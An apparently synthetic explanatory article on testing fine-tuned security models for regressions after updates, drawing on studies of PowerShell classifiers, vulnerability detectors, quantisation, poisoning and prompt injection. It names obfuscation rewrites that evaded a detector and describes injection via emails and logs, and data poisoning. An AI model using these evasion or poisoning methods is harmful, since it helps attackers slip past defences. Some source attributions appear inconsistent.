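# Managing updates to fine-tuned security models: re-testing and monitoring after each change

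## What a fine-tuned security model does and what counts as an update

A fine-tuned security model is a general-purpose machine-learning model trained further for a defensive task, such as flagging malicious scripts, malware, phishing messages or vulnerable code. Organisations update these models repeatedly because attackers change their methods and better base models appear. An update can raise a model's overall accuracy and still cause it to miss attacks it used to catch. Managing updates means testing for such losses before a new version goes into use and monitoring for new ones afterwards.

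### A model that screens PowerShell scripts

A security operations team might use a model to label PowerShell scripts as malicious or benign, then pass the alerts to analysts. PowerShell is a command-line shell and scripting language commonly used to automate system management. Attackers like it too, because it is already on the machines they break into. Its Invoke-WebRequest command fetches data from a web address, and Invoke-Expression runs text as code. Fetterman (2026), in *Inherited Circuits, Learned Semantics*, a study from Cisco's threat-research group Talos, points out that such commands also occur in harmless administrative scripts. A classifier therefore needs the surrounding context to tell malicious scripts from benign ones.

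*Defending at Machine-Speed*, by the security log search company Splunk, describes this workflow in use. A search picks suspicious scripts out of the logs, a language model labels each one, and an analyst reviews them with the labels in view. At five minutes per alert, an analyst would need 83 hours to get through a queue of 1,000, while the model labels the same queue in about 33 minutes. Cisco has run pilots in which a security model classifies alerts for its own incident-response staff.

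### Pre-training, fine-tuning and adapters

A language model consists largely of numbers called weights, often billions of them, and training sets their values. The developer first pre-trains the model to predict the next fragment of text in an enormous general collection of writing. Fine-tuning continues the training on a smaller, targeted set of examples, such as scripts with their correct labels. A fine-tuning round is one further training of an existing model that produces a new version.

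A model can go through several of these stages. Cisco's Foundation-Sec-8B-Instruct, which features in much of the research on PowerShell screening, began as Meta's Llama 3.1 8B, a model with about eight billion weights. *Llama-3.1-FoundationAI-SecurityLLM-8B-Instruct Technical Report* (Weerawardhena, Kassianik and colleagues, 2025) describes three further stages: more pre-training on security text, then fine-tuning on instructions with good answers, then training on preferences between answers. As Cisco says, none of this was aimed at PowerShell classification in particular, so results about Foundation-Sec are evidence about broad security training. *Defending at Machine Speed* (Fetterman) describes a narrower alternative, in which the small language model RoBERTa was trained only on PowerShell classification.

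Adjusting every weight is expensive, so many teams use low-rank adaptation (LoRA). LoRA leaves the original weights as they are and trains a small add-on, the adapter. For a table of weights W, the model uses

W′ = W + γBA

where A and B are two thin tables and γ is a constant that scales their effect. If W has 4,096 rows and 4,096 columns, it holds about 16.8 million weights. At rank 8, B has 8 columns and A has 8 rows, and together they hold 65,536 numbers. Thinking Machines' *LoRA Without Regret*, a study by an AI company, gives a total of three million trainable numbers for Llama 3.1 8B at rank 1. In its experiments LoRA matched full fine-tuning on small and medium datasets and fell behind once the data exceeded the adapter's capacity. For malware classification with written explanations, *Accuracy and Efficiency Trade-Offs in LLM-Based Malware Detection and Explanation* (2025) gives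 full fine-tuning the best overall scores for explanation quality, but a mid-sized LoRA version came close with over 80% less training time.

One server can hold several adapters at once, which makes it easy to try a new version or go back to an old one. But even a small adapter can change the model's behaviour substantially, because the added term BA is used in processing every script, including scripts unlike any in the new training data.

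### Test sets, thresholds and error rates

Developers split their labelled examples into three sets. They use the training set to adjust the model's weights, the validation set to make choices such as when to stop training, and the held-out set only for the final measurement. Held-out accuracy is the share of correct answers on the held-out set, whose examples come from the same source as the training data.

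*AutoMalDesc* (Apostu, Preda and colleagues, 2025) describes two successive rounds of LoRA fine-tuning at the security company CrowdStrike. The first round used 900 carefully checked scripts in five languages. The second added about 101,000 scripts that the first version had labelled. In both rounds, the developers used validation results to decide when to stop training, then tested the model on 3,636 held-out scripts. Average accuracy at detecting malware rose from 89.3% to 91.5% between the two versions, but accuracy on PowerShell stayed at 95.3%, so a team that screens only PowerShell would have seen no gain in detection accuracy.

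The held-out set also has to stay out of training, which is hard to ensure when teams assemble training data from public collections. Weerawardhena and colleagues checked one public security training set against a common benchmark and found that it contained between 75% and 92% of one group of the benchmark's questions, depending on the detection method. The training set's makers had built it partly from those questions.

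For each script, a classifier typically produces a score, and the decision threshold is the score above which the system raises an alert. A higher threshold means fewer false alarms and more missed attacks. Splunk tested the unmodified Llama 3 8B on 1,000 malicious and 1,000 benign scripts, and its published rates imply roughly these counts, leaving aside the 2.4% of scripts for which the model gave no usable label:

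| | Labelled malicious | Labelled benign |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious scripts | 1,000 | 0 |
| Benign scripts | 250 | 750 |

Recall is the share of malicious scripts the model catches, here 1,000 of 1,000, or 1.00. Precision is the share of alerts that are correct, here 1,000 of 1,250, or 0.80. The false-positive rate is the share of benign scripts that set off an alert, here 250 of 1,000, or 0.25.

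### What can change the model's behaviour

Anything that can alter the label a script receives counts as an update, whether or not anyone has retrained the model.

A round of fine-tuning is the most obvious kind of update, and some designs make it routine. *LoRA-based Parameter-Efficient LLMs for Continuous Learning in Edge-based Malware Detection* (2026) describes a detector that gains a new adapter for every two attack types introduced.

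Replacing the base model is a larger change, because an adapter fits only the weights it was trained with, so the team must fine-tune again. Base models also perform differently before any fine-tuning. Splunk gave three of them the same prompt and scripts. Recall was almost identical, but precision was 0.80 for Llama 3 and 0.70 for Google's Gemma. On the counts above, switching from Llama 3 to Gemma would raise false alarms from 250 to about 430.

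Editing the prompt, meaning the instructions and context that accompany each script, can change the results substantially without changing the weights. In *Defending at Machine Speed*, Fetterman first used Llama 3 with a plain prompt, then added to each prompt the two most similar scripts from a stored collection of malicious and benign examples. Accuracy rose from 0.86 to 0.93 and precision from 0.78 to 0.97, but recall fell from 1.00 to 0.89, so the system with the added examples missed about one malicious script in nine.

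Changing the threshold affects which scores raise an alert. Retraining can also change the alerts by moving the scores while the threshold stays the same, which is easier to overlook. *Churning Out Machine Learning Models* (Krisiloff, 2019), written at the security company FireEye, describes a hypothetical system that alerts on any web address scoring above 0.9, or above 0.5 if the address is also on a blocklist. If a retrained model gives every .com address a higher score, the same two thresholds produce a different set of alerts.

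Quantisation stores a model's weights at lower numerical precision, for example in 4 or 8 bits each instead of 16, to save memory and computing time. Rababah, Qamar and colleagues (2026) explain in *The Illusion of Equivalency* that the original and the compressed model can both score 75% even if 15% of the questions went from right to wrong and another 15% from wrong to right. In *The Noise Floor of a Quantization Comparison*, Blagojevich and Sunderland (2026) found this pattern in a model with 27 billion weights. On 31,275 questions, its 4-bit version gave six fewer correct answers than the original, because 436 answers got worse and 430 got better. The questions covered customer requests, reading comprehension and general knowledge, so the size of the effect on malicious scripts is unknown.

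In the same experiments, decisions also changed after steps that a team might not think to record. Out of 2,400 decisions, restarting the server with identical settings flipped between 0 and 22, and moving the uncompressed model to different serving software flipped between 6 and 16. The 4-bit versions flipped between 84 and 139. Merging a LoRA adapter into the main weights, a common step before release, also changes some answers, so a team that tests the separate adapter and ships the merged model has tested a slightly different model. *Chinese Decision* (2026) reports that merging changed 0.45% to 0.68% of top answers in three small models, compared with 0.81% to 1.08% for 8-bit quantisation.

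The last kind of update happens without the team's knowledge. Many organisations reach a model through a supplier's online service, and the supplier can replace the model, compress it or alter its hidden instructions. Abraham and Bucknall (2026), in *Silent Updates*, define a silent update as a change that materially affects what users see without public disclosure. A model's name can stay the same when the model changes, as "deepseek-chat" did through several versions, and only five of the nine suppliers they examined documented a fixed version that customers can keep using. Chauvin, Le Merrer and colleagues (2025), in *Log Probability Tracking of LLM APIs*, queried 189 hosted models every hour for more than four months and identified 37 suspected changes on 29 of them. No supplier confirmed a specific change, and the method does not distinguish a new model from new hardware or software.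 Chishti, Oyinloye and Li (2026), in *Test Before You Deploy*, do cite an official account, a 2025 incident report in which Anthropic described errors that misrouted up to 16% of requests to one of its models.

### Why security differs from ordinary classification

An attacker can rewrite a script until it gets past the detector, provided it still does the same thing. For instance, PowerShell accepts "iwr" as a short name for Invoke-WebRequest, so Fetterman could swap one for the other without affecting what a script does. A held-out set contains only the disguises that were in its source. Apostu and colleagues put the share of deliberately obscured scripts in their source at 6% or more. Old attacks also stay in circulation. *Regression-aware Continual Learning for Android Malware Detection* (2025) argues that attackers can reuse old malware or modify it slightly, so an update that makes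 the model stop detecting it reopens a gap the defenders had closed.

Malicious inputs are usually rare, so a model's precision is lower in use than on a balanced test. If one script in 1,000 is malicious and the model screens 100,000 of them, it would catch all 100 attacks but, at the false-positive rate in the table, raise almost 25,000 false alarms, for a precision of 0.4%. Fetterman's specialised RoBERTa model scored 0.99 for precision and 0.98 for recall on a balanced sample, which implies a false-positive rate of about 1%. On the same 100,000 scripts, it would catch 98 attacks and raise about 1,000 false alarms, for a precision of about 9%. A change of half a percentage point in the false-positive rate would be easy to miss in a test report, but it would add or remove about 500 alerts.

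Correct labels are slow and expensive to obtain. Apostu and colleagues labelled their 900 starting scripts by combining pattern-matching rules, trial runs in an isolated environment and manual checks by experts. They had automatic labels for the other 157,000 but judged those labels too unreliable to train on. In daily use, analysts who look only at alerts will correct false alarms but miss attacks that the model labelled benign. An investigation may uncover those attacks months later, or they may never be found.

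### Data drift and regression

A detector can get worse because of data drift or because of an update. Data drift is a change over time in the inputs a deployed model receives, or in how those inputs relate to the correct labels. For example, recall can fall without any change to the model when a new attack tool produces scripts unlike any in the training data. A decline caused by an update is called a regression. *Robustness-Congruent Adversarial Training for Secure Machine Learning Model Updates* (2024) takes the term from software development, where it means that something works less well after an update than before. Identifying a regression requires comparing the current model, which is the version in use, with the candidate model, which is the updated version proposed to replace it. A malicious script that the current model catches and the candidate misses is a security regression.

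Drift is a main reason to retrain a model, but retraining can cause regressions. Krisiloff trained a detector on Windows program files from a public collection, using those first seen from January to August 2017, then retrained it with the first version's mistakes from September and October added. On files from November and December, accuracy rose from 99.10% to 99.33%, but the retrained detector got 246 files wrong that the first version had got right. These errors may have included both false alarms and missed malware. The detector was a set of decision trees, not a language model, but with either, a team that doesn't retrain is exposed to new threats, and retraining may bring back some old errors.

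A team can distinguish the effects of an update from those of drift by holding either the inputs or the model fixed. Drift cannot explain a difference between the old and new models' answers to the same inputs, and an update cannot explain a decline when one unchanged model processes inputs from successive months. If a supplier replaces the model without telling the team, the second comparison is invalid and the team mistakes a regression for drift.

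For each update, the team first records what changed and decides how much to re-test. It then builds or extends a regression suite, a fixed set of test cases that includes rewritten attacks, and compares the current and candidate models on each case. A team with access to the weights can also check whether training changed how the model uses evidence. The team repairs what got worse, tests again, and adopts the candidate only if the model meets conditions set before testing. After release, the team monitors the model until the next change.

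## Why a higher held-out score can hide a weaker detector

Held-out accuracy is an average over the held-out set, so a gain on common inputs can outweigh a loss on rare ones. Suppose a team tests its current model and a candidate on 1,000 malicious and 1,000 benign scripts, and 60 of the malicious scripts are disguised, roughly the share that Apostu and colleagues estimated for their source. The current model catches every malicious script and raises 100 false alarms, for an accuracy of 95%. The candidate misses 30 of the 60 disguised scripts but raises only 40 false alarms, so its accuracy is higher, at 96.5%.

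A held-out set also shares the quirks of the training data. If Invoke-WebRequest is written in full in nearly every malicious script in a collection, a model can learn to rely on that spelling and will still do well on the held-out scripts, which have the same spelling. An attacker can then defeat the model with a behaviour-preserving transformation, a rewrite that changes how a script looks but not what it does. Two studies from 2026 tested models fine-tuned for security for this weakness, one using malicious scripts and the other vulnerable code.

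### Foundation-Sec and Llama on disguised scripts

Fetterman compared Cisco's security model, Foundation-Sec-8B-Instruct, with Meta's Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, a general-purpose chat model of the same size and design. The accuracy test used 74 pairs of PowerShell scripts. Each pair matched a malicious script with a benign one containing the same kind of suspicious command, so neither model could do well by spotting the command alone. Foundation-Sec classified all 148 scripts correctly, and Llama classified 141 correctly (95.3%). Llama scored lower because it raised more false alarms on benign scripts. Foundation-Sec had no real advantage in catching attacks.

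For the second test, Fetterman took malicious scripts that the model already classified correctly, called seeds, and rewrote them as variants that did the same thing. The first of three tiers replaced visible commands with direct equivalents, such as "iwr" for Invoke-WebRequest. The second hid commands by having the script assemble them as it ran. The third changed only capitalization, which PowerShell ignores in command names.

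Foundation-Sec missed 6 of 44 variants in the first tier, 4 of 46 in the second and 9 of 63 in the third. Llama missed none of the 153. If a team replaced Llama with Foundation-Sec, each of the 19 misses would be a security regression, and the accuracy test would have given no hint of them. The misses cluster in a few techniques:

| Tier | Rewrite | Foundation-Sec misses |
|---|---|---|
| Direct | Short name for Invoke-WebRequest | 4 of 4 |
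| Direct | Indirect call to DownloadString, which fetches text from the web | 2 of 6 |
| Direct | All others | 0 of 34 |
| Assembled | Invoke-Expression built from pieces of text | 4 of 4 |
| Assembled | All others | 0 of 42 |
| Letter case | Invoke-Expression in alternating case | 4 of 4 |
| Letter case | Invoke-Expression in lower case | 1 of 4 |
| Letter case | IEX, short for Invoke-Expression, in changed case | 4 of 4 |
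| Letter case | All others | 0 of 51 |

Four rewrites evaded detection every time and account for 16 of the 19 misses. How heavily a rewrite disguised the script did not predict the result. Foundation-Sec caught every script that recovered its commands from encoded text, but missed scripts in which only the capitalization had changed. It also caught all 127 variants made with the remaining techniques. A test that sampled a few disguised scripts at random could easily have missed these failures, so a useful test has to cover each important command with each kind of rewrite.

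### How far fine-tuning explains the misses

The groups are so small that four misses out of four are compatible with a true miss rate anywhere from about 40% to 100%. The three groups of Invoke-Expression variants have four members each and may share the same four seed scripts. If they do, a peculiarity of those scripts could account for nine of the misses. Fetterman therefore treats the results as priorities for further testing, not as estimates of how often attackers would succeed.

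Using only seed scripts that the model classified correctly makes it easy to attribute a later miss to the rewrite, but it leaves out every attack that the model missed before any rewriting. The overall miss rate of 12% therefore can't be generalized to scripts in daily use. Selection may also have affected the accuracy test. Fetterman's main collection kept only the 293 of 380 candidate pairs in which both scripts were classified correctly at the start. If the 74 pairs came from that collection, Foundation-Sec's perfect score is partly a result of that selection.

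Fetterman also measured the gain and the misses with different prompts, so the two results do not describe one system that a team could deploy. The 4.7-point gain came from a prompt that told the model to judge a script's overall purpose, and the 19 misses came from a plainer one. The purpose prompt removed some misses and produced others, so the weakness does not come from the plain prompt alone.

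Llama may have missed no variants because it is more inclined to call a script malicious. Every variant was malicious, so a model that labelled everything malicious would also have missed none. In the accuracy test, Llama's extra errors were false alarms. Its scores also leaned further towards "malicious", with an average gap of 8.15 between its scores for the two labels, against 3.75 for Foundation-Sec. A script rewrite that reduced the gap by five would reverse Foundation-Sec's typical answer but not Llama's. To separate robustness from this tendency, a tester would add disguised benign scripts and compare the models at thresholds that give them the same false-positive rate.

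This lean does not seem to be the whole explanation, because 17 of the 19 misses involved just two commands, Invoke-WebRequest and Invoke-Expression. A smaller margin on every script should have produced misses across many techniques. Fetterman's study of the models' internals also suggests a change in how Foundation-Sec uses the evidence from particular commands.

Even if Foundation-Sec is the more brittle model, security training is only one possible cause. Fetterman calls Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct the base model and Foundation-Sec its fine-tuned version, but the development history that Weerawardhena and colleagues give makes the two siblings:

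- Llama 3.1 8B, then Meta's own chat training, gives Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct.
- Llama 3.1 8B, then further pre-training on security text, then Cisco's own chat training, gives Foundation-Sec-8B-Instruct.

The brittleness could come from the security text or from Cisco's chat training. Alternatively, Meta's chat training may have given Llama robustness that Foundation-Sec never gained. Fetterman's explanation is that a model learns to link certain command names with the label "malicious" when they often appear together in its training data. Yet Cisco did not train Foundation-Sec specifically to classify PowerShell, and its developers relied mainly on pre-training rather than chat training for security knowledge. The explanation is plausible, but comparing the finished models can't confirm it.

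A cleaner experiment would start from one model and train two versions with the same method, one on security text and the other on an equal amount of ordinary text. Fetterman studied only one pair of models, so repeating the experiment with others would show whether the effect is general. A team that updates its own model has an easier task because it usually has both the current model and the candidate that came from it, and it can record every change between them.

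### Vulnerable code and its patch

A vulnerable function that its developers have since fixed is an especially hard case for a detector of vulnerable code. Huang, Sun and colleagues (2026) built the TrapEval evaluation around this case in *Do Fine-Tuned LLMs Understand Vulnerabilities?* They merged three public collections of C and C++ functions from real projects and made two datasets, each with the same 24,747 vulnerable functions and 19,418 safe ones. The safe functions were patched versions of vulnerable functions in the first dataset and ordinary functions unrelated to the flaws in the second.

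The researchers used LoRA to fine-tune five open models with roughly seven to eight billion parameters each: two Qwen models, two DeepSeek models, and Llama 3.1 8B. They trained on 90% of each dataset and tested on the rest. They trained one version of each model to give only a label and another to write out its reasoning first, using explanations from a stronger model that had been given the correct answer.

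Their main measure is F1, which combines precision P and recall R in one number:

F1 = 2PR / (P + R)

The five label-only models gave these results:

| Safe code in training | Safe code in testing | F1 | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unrelated | Unrelated | 78–84% | 80–85% | 22–30% |
| Unrelated | Patched | 72–73% | 97–98% | 94–95% |
| Patched | Patched | 59–68% | 57–78% | 46–68% |

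The models trained with unrelated safe code looked strong on the usual kind of test, which uses data like their training data. On patched functions, the same models raised a false alarm about 94% of the time. They had apparently learned to recognise the kind of function in which flaws occur, and repairing the flaw barely changed their answers.

F1 does little to reveal this failure. The published rates imply that about 57% of the functions in the patched test were vulnerable. A program that labelled every function vulnerable would therefore have an F1 of about 73%, the same as the fine-tuned models. Models trained on patched code had a lower F1 even though they raised fewer false alarms, so a team that compared only F1 would prefer the models that flagged nearly everything.

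The 94% figure may be higher than it would be for unfamiliar code. Both datasets contain the same vulnerable functions, yet the same models found about 84% of those in one test and 97% of those in the other. The two tests must therefore have contained different vulnerable functions, and some of those in the patched test were probably in the models' training data. A model that has memorized a vulnerable function is likely to flag its nearly identical patch. In practice, a detector trained on published vulnerabilities will often have to scan the repaired versions.

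Huang and colleagues tested Qwen3-8B before and after fine-tuning with written reasoning. On unrelated code, recall rose from 27% to 61% while the false-positive rate rose only from 20% to 27%, so the model became much better at telling vulnerable code from safe code. On patched code, recall rose from 28% to 49%, but the false-positive rate rose almost as much, from 25% to 43%, so most of the change came from the model answering "vulnerable" more often.

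Huang and colleagues then rewrote each test function in seven ways that leave its logic intact: renaming its parameters, renaming the function, or adding comments, spaces, line breaks, an unused function or code that never runs. The F1 of the label-only models fell by 3.86 to 7.21 points, so edits with no bearing on security can change a fine-tuned detector's answers. The drop doesn't show how many vulnerable functions the models missed, because F1 combines missed flaws with false alarms. It also doesn't show that fine-tuning caused the fragility, because the researchers didn't test the rewritten functions on any model that hadn't been fine-tuned.

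Training on written reasoning made the models steadier. Their F1 mostly fell by no more than 1.12 points on the rewritten functions, and in some cases it rose slightly. Reasoning also cut the false-positive rate on patches from 94% to 65% for Llama 3.1 8B trained on unrelated code. But it lowered recall. When both training and testing used patched code, the general DeepSeek model found 73% of vulnerable functions after training on labels alone and 46% after training with reasoning. Huang and colleagues suggest that a model answers "safe" when it can't construct a complete argument for a flaw.

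The reasoning models were steadier but did not perform better overall. On the test with unrelated code, every label-only model would still have a higher F1 than its reasoning counterpart after losing 7.21 points, the largest reported loss. A team choosing between the two types would have to decide whether fewer false alarms on patched code are worth more missed vulnerabilities, and a test of stability under rewriting would not answer that question.

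TrapEval also measured whether larger edits made patches easier to recognise. Trained on labels alone, Qwen3-8B had an F1 of 50% on nearly identical pairs and 63% on the most different ones. All five models showed some dependence on edit size, but it was weak, with correlations between 0.03 and 0.07 in magnitude. Small patches are also harder for any reader to recognise, so the pattern is only slight evidence that the models judge by the amount of changed text. Models trained with reasoning showed no detectable dependence, though Huang and colleagues warn that these models' low scores could hide one.

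The written explanations are of limited help in judging whether a model understood a flaw. Another language model sorted the failed explanations into eight types of error. False alarms often involved misreading control flow (the order in which code runs) or inventing behaviour for library functions. Missed vulnerabilities more often involved misapplying the definition of the weakness or confusion about operations that run at the same time. This sorting depends on a single model's judgement, and the explanations may not match how the detector reached its label.

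Wrong labels in the data may account for part of the poor result on patches. The collections infer labels from developers' vulnerability fixes, and Huang and colleagues say only that more than half of the labels in each collection are accurate. If a fix changed several functions but only one was dangerous, the others may be wrongly labeled "vulnerable", and no detector could tell their old and new versions apart on security grounds. Larger models might also do better. But the false-positive rates on unrelated and patched code differ by more than 60 points, which is a strong reason to test any vulnerability detector on patched code too.

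### Lost refusals and unstable safety scores

Fine-tuning can also change behaviour that the detection task never exercises. Developers train chat models to refuse harmful requests, and further training can weaken those refusals. This matters little if the detector can output only a label, but more if the same model also answers analysts' questions or writes code for them.

Fraser, Dawkins and colleagues (2025), in *Fine-Tuning Lowers Safety and Disrupts Evaluation Consistency*, studied 150 fine-tuned versions of two small models from Meta and Mistral. The training data consisted of general questions and answers, with safety-related questions removed. They gave each version 440 unsafe requests and used another model to judge which ones it fulfilled. For every combination of model and dataset, fine-tuning substantially increased the share of unsafe requests the model fulfilled.

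The size of the increase varied between training runs. In the most extreme case, changing only the random seed, a number that fixes the random choices made in training, gave harmfulness scores of 0.73 and 0.82, a difference of about 40 requests out of 440. Part of this difference may come from randomness in the answers, since repeated tests of an unchanged model also gave different scores. A team that trains one candidate and tests it once could mistake this variation for the effect of an update.

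Fraser and colleagues also trained the Meta model on its own answers to the same questions. This did far less damage, which suggests that most of the loss comes from new content in the training data rather than from fine-tuning itself. The experiment used general data, but security datasets are likely to contain much that is new to a chat model.

*Safety Measurements for Fine-tuned LLMs Should be Grounded in Capability* (2026) combined requests from several benchmarks and varied the judge, and found that conclusions about the effects of fine-tuning depended on the choice of requests and judge. A team comparing a candidate with the current model therefore needs to test both with the same requests, judge and generation settings, and repeat the tests enough times to show the normal variation.

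A model can stay willing to refuse malicious requests after security training when its developers include good general chat training. Weerawardhena and colleagues gave Foundation-Sec-8B-Instruct 400 malicious requests, and it refused or answered safely 92% of the time, clearly more often than Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct. Adding a separate filtering model raised the figure to 99%. Cisco had given its model no dedicated safety training beyond its ordinary chat training.

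The content of the training examples can change how a model answers unrelated questions. Costa and Vicente (2026), in *Persona-Model Collapse in Emergent Misalignment*, fine-tuned four large models to write insecure code and trained matched versions on secure code. Insecure-code training lowered GPT-4.1's score from 93.3 to 41.9 on a 100-point scale of how well a model's answers to unrelated questions agree with human values, while secure-code training left it at 93.6. The two Qwen models also lost points after secure-code training, but far fewer than after insecure-code training. None of the four showed a detectable loss on a general knowledge test after insecure-code training, so a team that tested only knowledge would have missed the change.

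Those models learned to produce vulnerable code, whereas a detector learns to label it, so the finding doesn't show that training a detector on such code has the same effect. It is more relevant to teams that train a single assistant both to find flaws and to write attack code for testing.

### Instructions hidden in logs and emails

A security model reads text that attackers write, which exposes it to prompt injection, where an attacker places instructions in that text hoping the model will follow them. A phishing email might contain a line telling any automated reader to classify the message as safe. A log entry can contain such a line too, because logs often record text that outsiders supply, such as a username or a web address.

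*CyberLLMInstruct* (ElZemity, Arief and Li, 2025) reports the largest measured losses in a security-tuned model. The researchers fine-tuned seven open models on 54,928 security instructions and responses, and used automated attack prompts to score each model before and after, from 0 (completely vulnerable) to 1 (fully secure). Scores for resistance to prompt injection fell from between 0.80 and 0.95 to between 0.15 and 0.40. Llama 3.1 8B fell furthest, from 0.95 to 0.15, while its accuracy on 10,000 security questions rose from 71% to 89%.

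The contrast between knowledge and resistance is striking, but the experiment was severe. The training data deliberately included phishing material, malware code and other malicious content, and each model went through the data ten times. ElZemity and colleagues acknowledge that, without a matched version trained only on harmless security text, the experiment can't separate the effect of the malicious examples from that of security training in general. The attacks were also prompts to a chat model, not instructions buried in an email or log that a detector had to classify.

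Part of the measured improvement in some models' accuracy may also come from better formatting rather than greater knowledge of security. Phi 3 Mini, a small model, rose from 5% to 19% on the 10,000 questions, which is still below the 25% expected from guessing among four options. Scores that low suggest that the model often failed to answer in the expected format.

Restoring refusals does not necessarily restore resistance to injected instructions. In *LLM360 K2* (2025), safety training raised the average share of safe responses from an open 65-billion-parameter model by 26 percentage points, to 77%, but raised its score on a prompt-injection test only from 54.6% to 56.6%. Refusing a user's harmful request and ignoring a harmless-looking command inside an email are different skills, so a team has to test them separately.

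An attacker who can influence the training data can compromise a model with biased examples alone, without hidden instructions. In *On The Dangers of Poisoned LLMs In Security Automation*, Karlsen and Eilertsen (2025) fine-tuned Llama 3.1 8B and Qwen3 4B to investigate security alerts. Biased examples in the training data made the models consistently dismiss genuine alerts about one user, even though the fine-tuned models appeared to be improvements. A held-out set would not reveal the problem if that user never appeared in it. If the set came from the same poisoned data, its labels might even mark the dismissals as correct.

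Narrow fine-tuning can make a model harder to manipulate when it starts from a pre-trained model with no instruction training. *Securing Large Language Models (LLMs) from Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) tested JATMO, a method that teaches such a model a single task. Because the model has never learned to follow instructions in general, it is less likely to obey instructions in its input. On a summarisation task, injections succeeded substantially less often against these models than against instruction-tuned ones, though some still succeeded.

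The same reasoning favours small classifiers for screening. Fetterman's RoBERTa model outputs a label and was not trained to follow instructions, so it classifies a sentence addressed to it like any other text. An attacker could still try to disguise the script itself. A chat model may be more useful when analysts want explanations, but each update then requires testing both its labels and its resistance to prompt injection.

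### What held-out accuracy still measures

Held-out accuracy is still a good estimate of how a detector will perform on undisguised inputs like those in the source of the held-out set. Such inputs make up most of what a detector sees, and small changes in the false-positive rate greatly affect analysts' work. If all seven of Llama's errors in the 74-pair test were false alarms, its false-positive rate there was about 9%, compared with zero for Foundation-Sec. The rate would differ on ordinary scripts, because Fetterman chose benign scripts that contained suspicious commands.

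A held-out test is also the easiest way to check whether a round of fine-tuning taught the model anything useful. Before fine-tuning, Qwen3-8B missed almost three-quarters of the vulnerable functions in TrapEval's test with unrelated code. Testing it on rewritten functions would have shown little at that stage, because it already missed most flaws in their original form and had few correct detections to lose.

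Accuracy and robustness can also improve together. *AQUA-LLM* (2025) compared models on security questions before and after fine-tuning and quantisation. Fine-tuning alone raised accuracy but often made the models easier to mislead with adversarial prompts, whereas fine-tuning combined with quantisation improved both accuracy and robustness. The task was answering questions, so the result doesn't show that the same combination would help a malware detector. Still, a team can't infer a loss of robustness from a gain in accuracy and has to measure both.

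The held-out set must also resemble the work the model will do. Weerawardhena and colleagues report that Foundation-Sec scored 0.69 and Llama scored 0.56 on matching vulnerability reports to types of weakness. On SecBench, a broader test of security knowledge, Foundation-Sec scored 0.69 and Llama scored 0.72. A team that needs help sorting vulnerability reports would have good reason to choose Foundation-Sec, but a team that wants a general adviser might not. Neither benchmark measures how well a model detects malicious scripts.

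## Recording each change and deciding how much to re-test

To compare a candidate with the current model, a team has to know exactly what each version consists of and be able to run both. The team keeps this information in a change record, which it opens before training and completes after deciding whether to release. The record covers the weights and everything else that can affect a script's label. The team also uses it to decide how much to re-test.

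### What to store, and what goes wrong without it

The team stores the weights together with a cryptographic hash, a short fingerprint calculated from the file that changes if any part of the file changes. The stored weights let the team restore the old version, and the hash lets it check that the file it tested is the one now in use. LoRA adapters take little storage. An eight-billion-weight model takes about 16 gigabytes at 16 bits per weight, while a rank-16 adapter for Llama 3.1 8B takes about 0.1 gigabytes, based on Thinking Machines' count of trainable weights. A year of monthly adapters would need little more than one gigabyte.

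An adapter is useless without its base model, so the record needs the base model's exact version and hash. If the record gives only a general name and the publisher later replaces a file under that name, the team may load an old adapter onto the wrong weights. They might not notice, because the result may still run and give plausible labels. The team should also keep its own copy of the base model in case the publisher withdraws it.

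The training data snapshot is a frozen copy of the examples and their labels. A link to a public collection isn't enough, because its maintainers add scripts and correct labels. Without a snapshot, the team can't check whether a test script was also a training example, or trace bad data later. The European standards body ETSI, in its standard *Baseline Cyber Security Requirements for AI Models and Systems* (2025), recommends recording where public training data came from and when the developer obtained it. If a source is later reported as poisoned, the developer can then tell whether the model learned from it. Scripts from an organisation's own logs may contain passwords or personal data, so the snapshot needs strict access controls. The team should store the training settings and random seed with the snapshot, because Fraser and colleagues found that changing the seed alone could noticeably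 change a model's behaviour.

Test results are hard to interpret without the prompt that produced them. Foundation-Sec missed different variants under Fetterman's two prompts, so a team that reworded the prompt between tests could wrongly attribute the difference in results to the weights. If the system adds similar scripts to each prompt, the team also has to store the collection those scripts come from. If the threshold isn't recorded, the team might restore a version that ran at 0.6 with a threshold of 0.5, see more alerts, and conclude that the incoming scripts have changed.

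Decoding settings control how a language model picks each token, or fragment of text, in its answer. At a temperature of zero, it always picks the highest-scoring token. At higher temperatures, it sometimes picks another, so the same script can get different labels in two runs. A team that doesn't know the temperature may mistake this difference for the effect of an update. The record should also give any length limit on the input, because if the system cuts off long scripts, a malicious command after the cut never reaches the model.

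The inference software loads the weights and runs the model. Its version matters, as do the numerical precision and the type of hardware, because Blagojevich and Sunderland saw labels flip when they moved an unchanged model to different software. A team that left these details out of its records would attribute such flips to training.

Finally, the record needs to include the version of the regression suite and each model's answer and score for every case. Individual results are necessary because two models with equal totals can miss different attacks. Without the suite version, a fall in recall from 97% to 94% could just mean that someone added harder cases.

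One way to find gaps in a record is to ask a colleague who didn't write it to rebuild the current version from it and run a few hundred cases. If the rebuilt version's labels differ from the deployed system's more than the deployed system's own labels vary between ordinary runs, the record is missing something.

### A scale of re-testing

A change needs more testing when it can affect more of the model's answers and when the team is less able to predict which ones. In the table, the counts out of 2,400 decisions come from Blagojevich and Sunderland, who did not test malicious scripts. The recall figures come from Fetterman's experiment with retrieved examples.

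| Change | Minimum re-test | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Decision threshold | Recalculate labels from stored scores, for the whole suite and for recent logs | The scores stay the same, so the team can count every changed label without running the model |
| Server restart or new inference software | Run the whole suite and compare the number of flips with normal variation | Unchanged weights flipped up to 22 of 2,400 decisions |
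| Quantisation or merging an adapter | Whole suite and held-out set, on the exact files for release | 4-bit versions flipped 84 to 139 of 2,400 decisions, and gains can hide losses in the total |
| Prompt, retrieved examples or decoding settings | Whole suite, held-out set and prompt-injection tests | Adding two examples to each prompt cut recall from 1.00 to 0.89 |
| Fine-tuning round on the same base model | The tests for a prompt change, a check of the threshold and newly written variants | Training can change the answer to any script, and new weaknesses may lie outside the old suite |
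| New base model | The tests for a fine-tuning round, a fresh choice of prompt and threshold, and a trial on live scripts beside the current model | Knowledge of the old model's weaknesses may no longer apply, and flips can occur anywhere |

A threshold edit needs the least re-testing because it can't both add and remove alerts. Lowering the threshold, for example, can't create a miss, so it is a reasonable emergency measure during an attack if analysts can handle the extra alerts.

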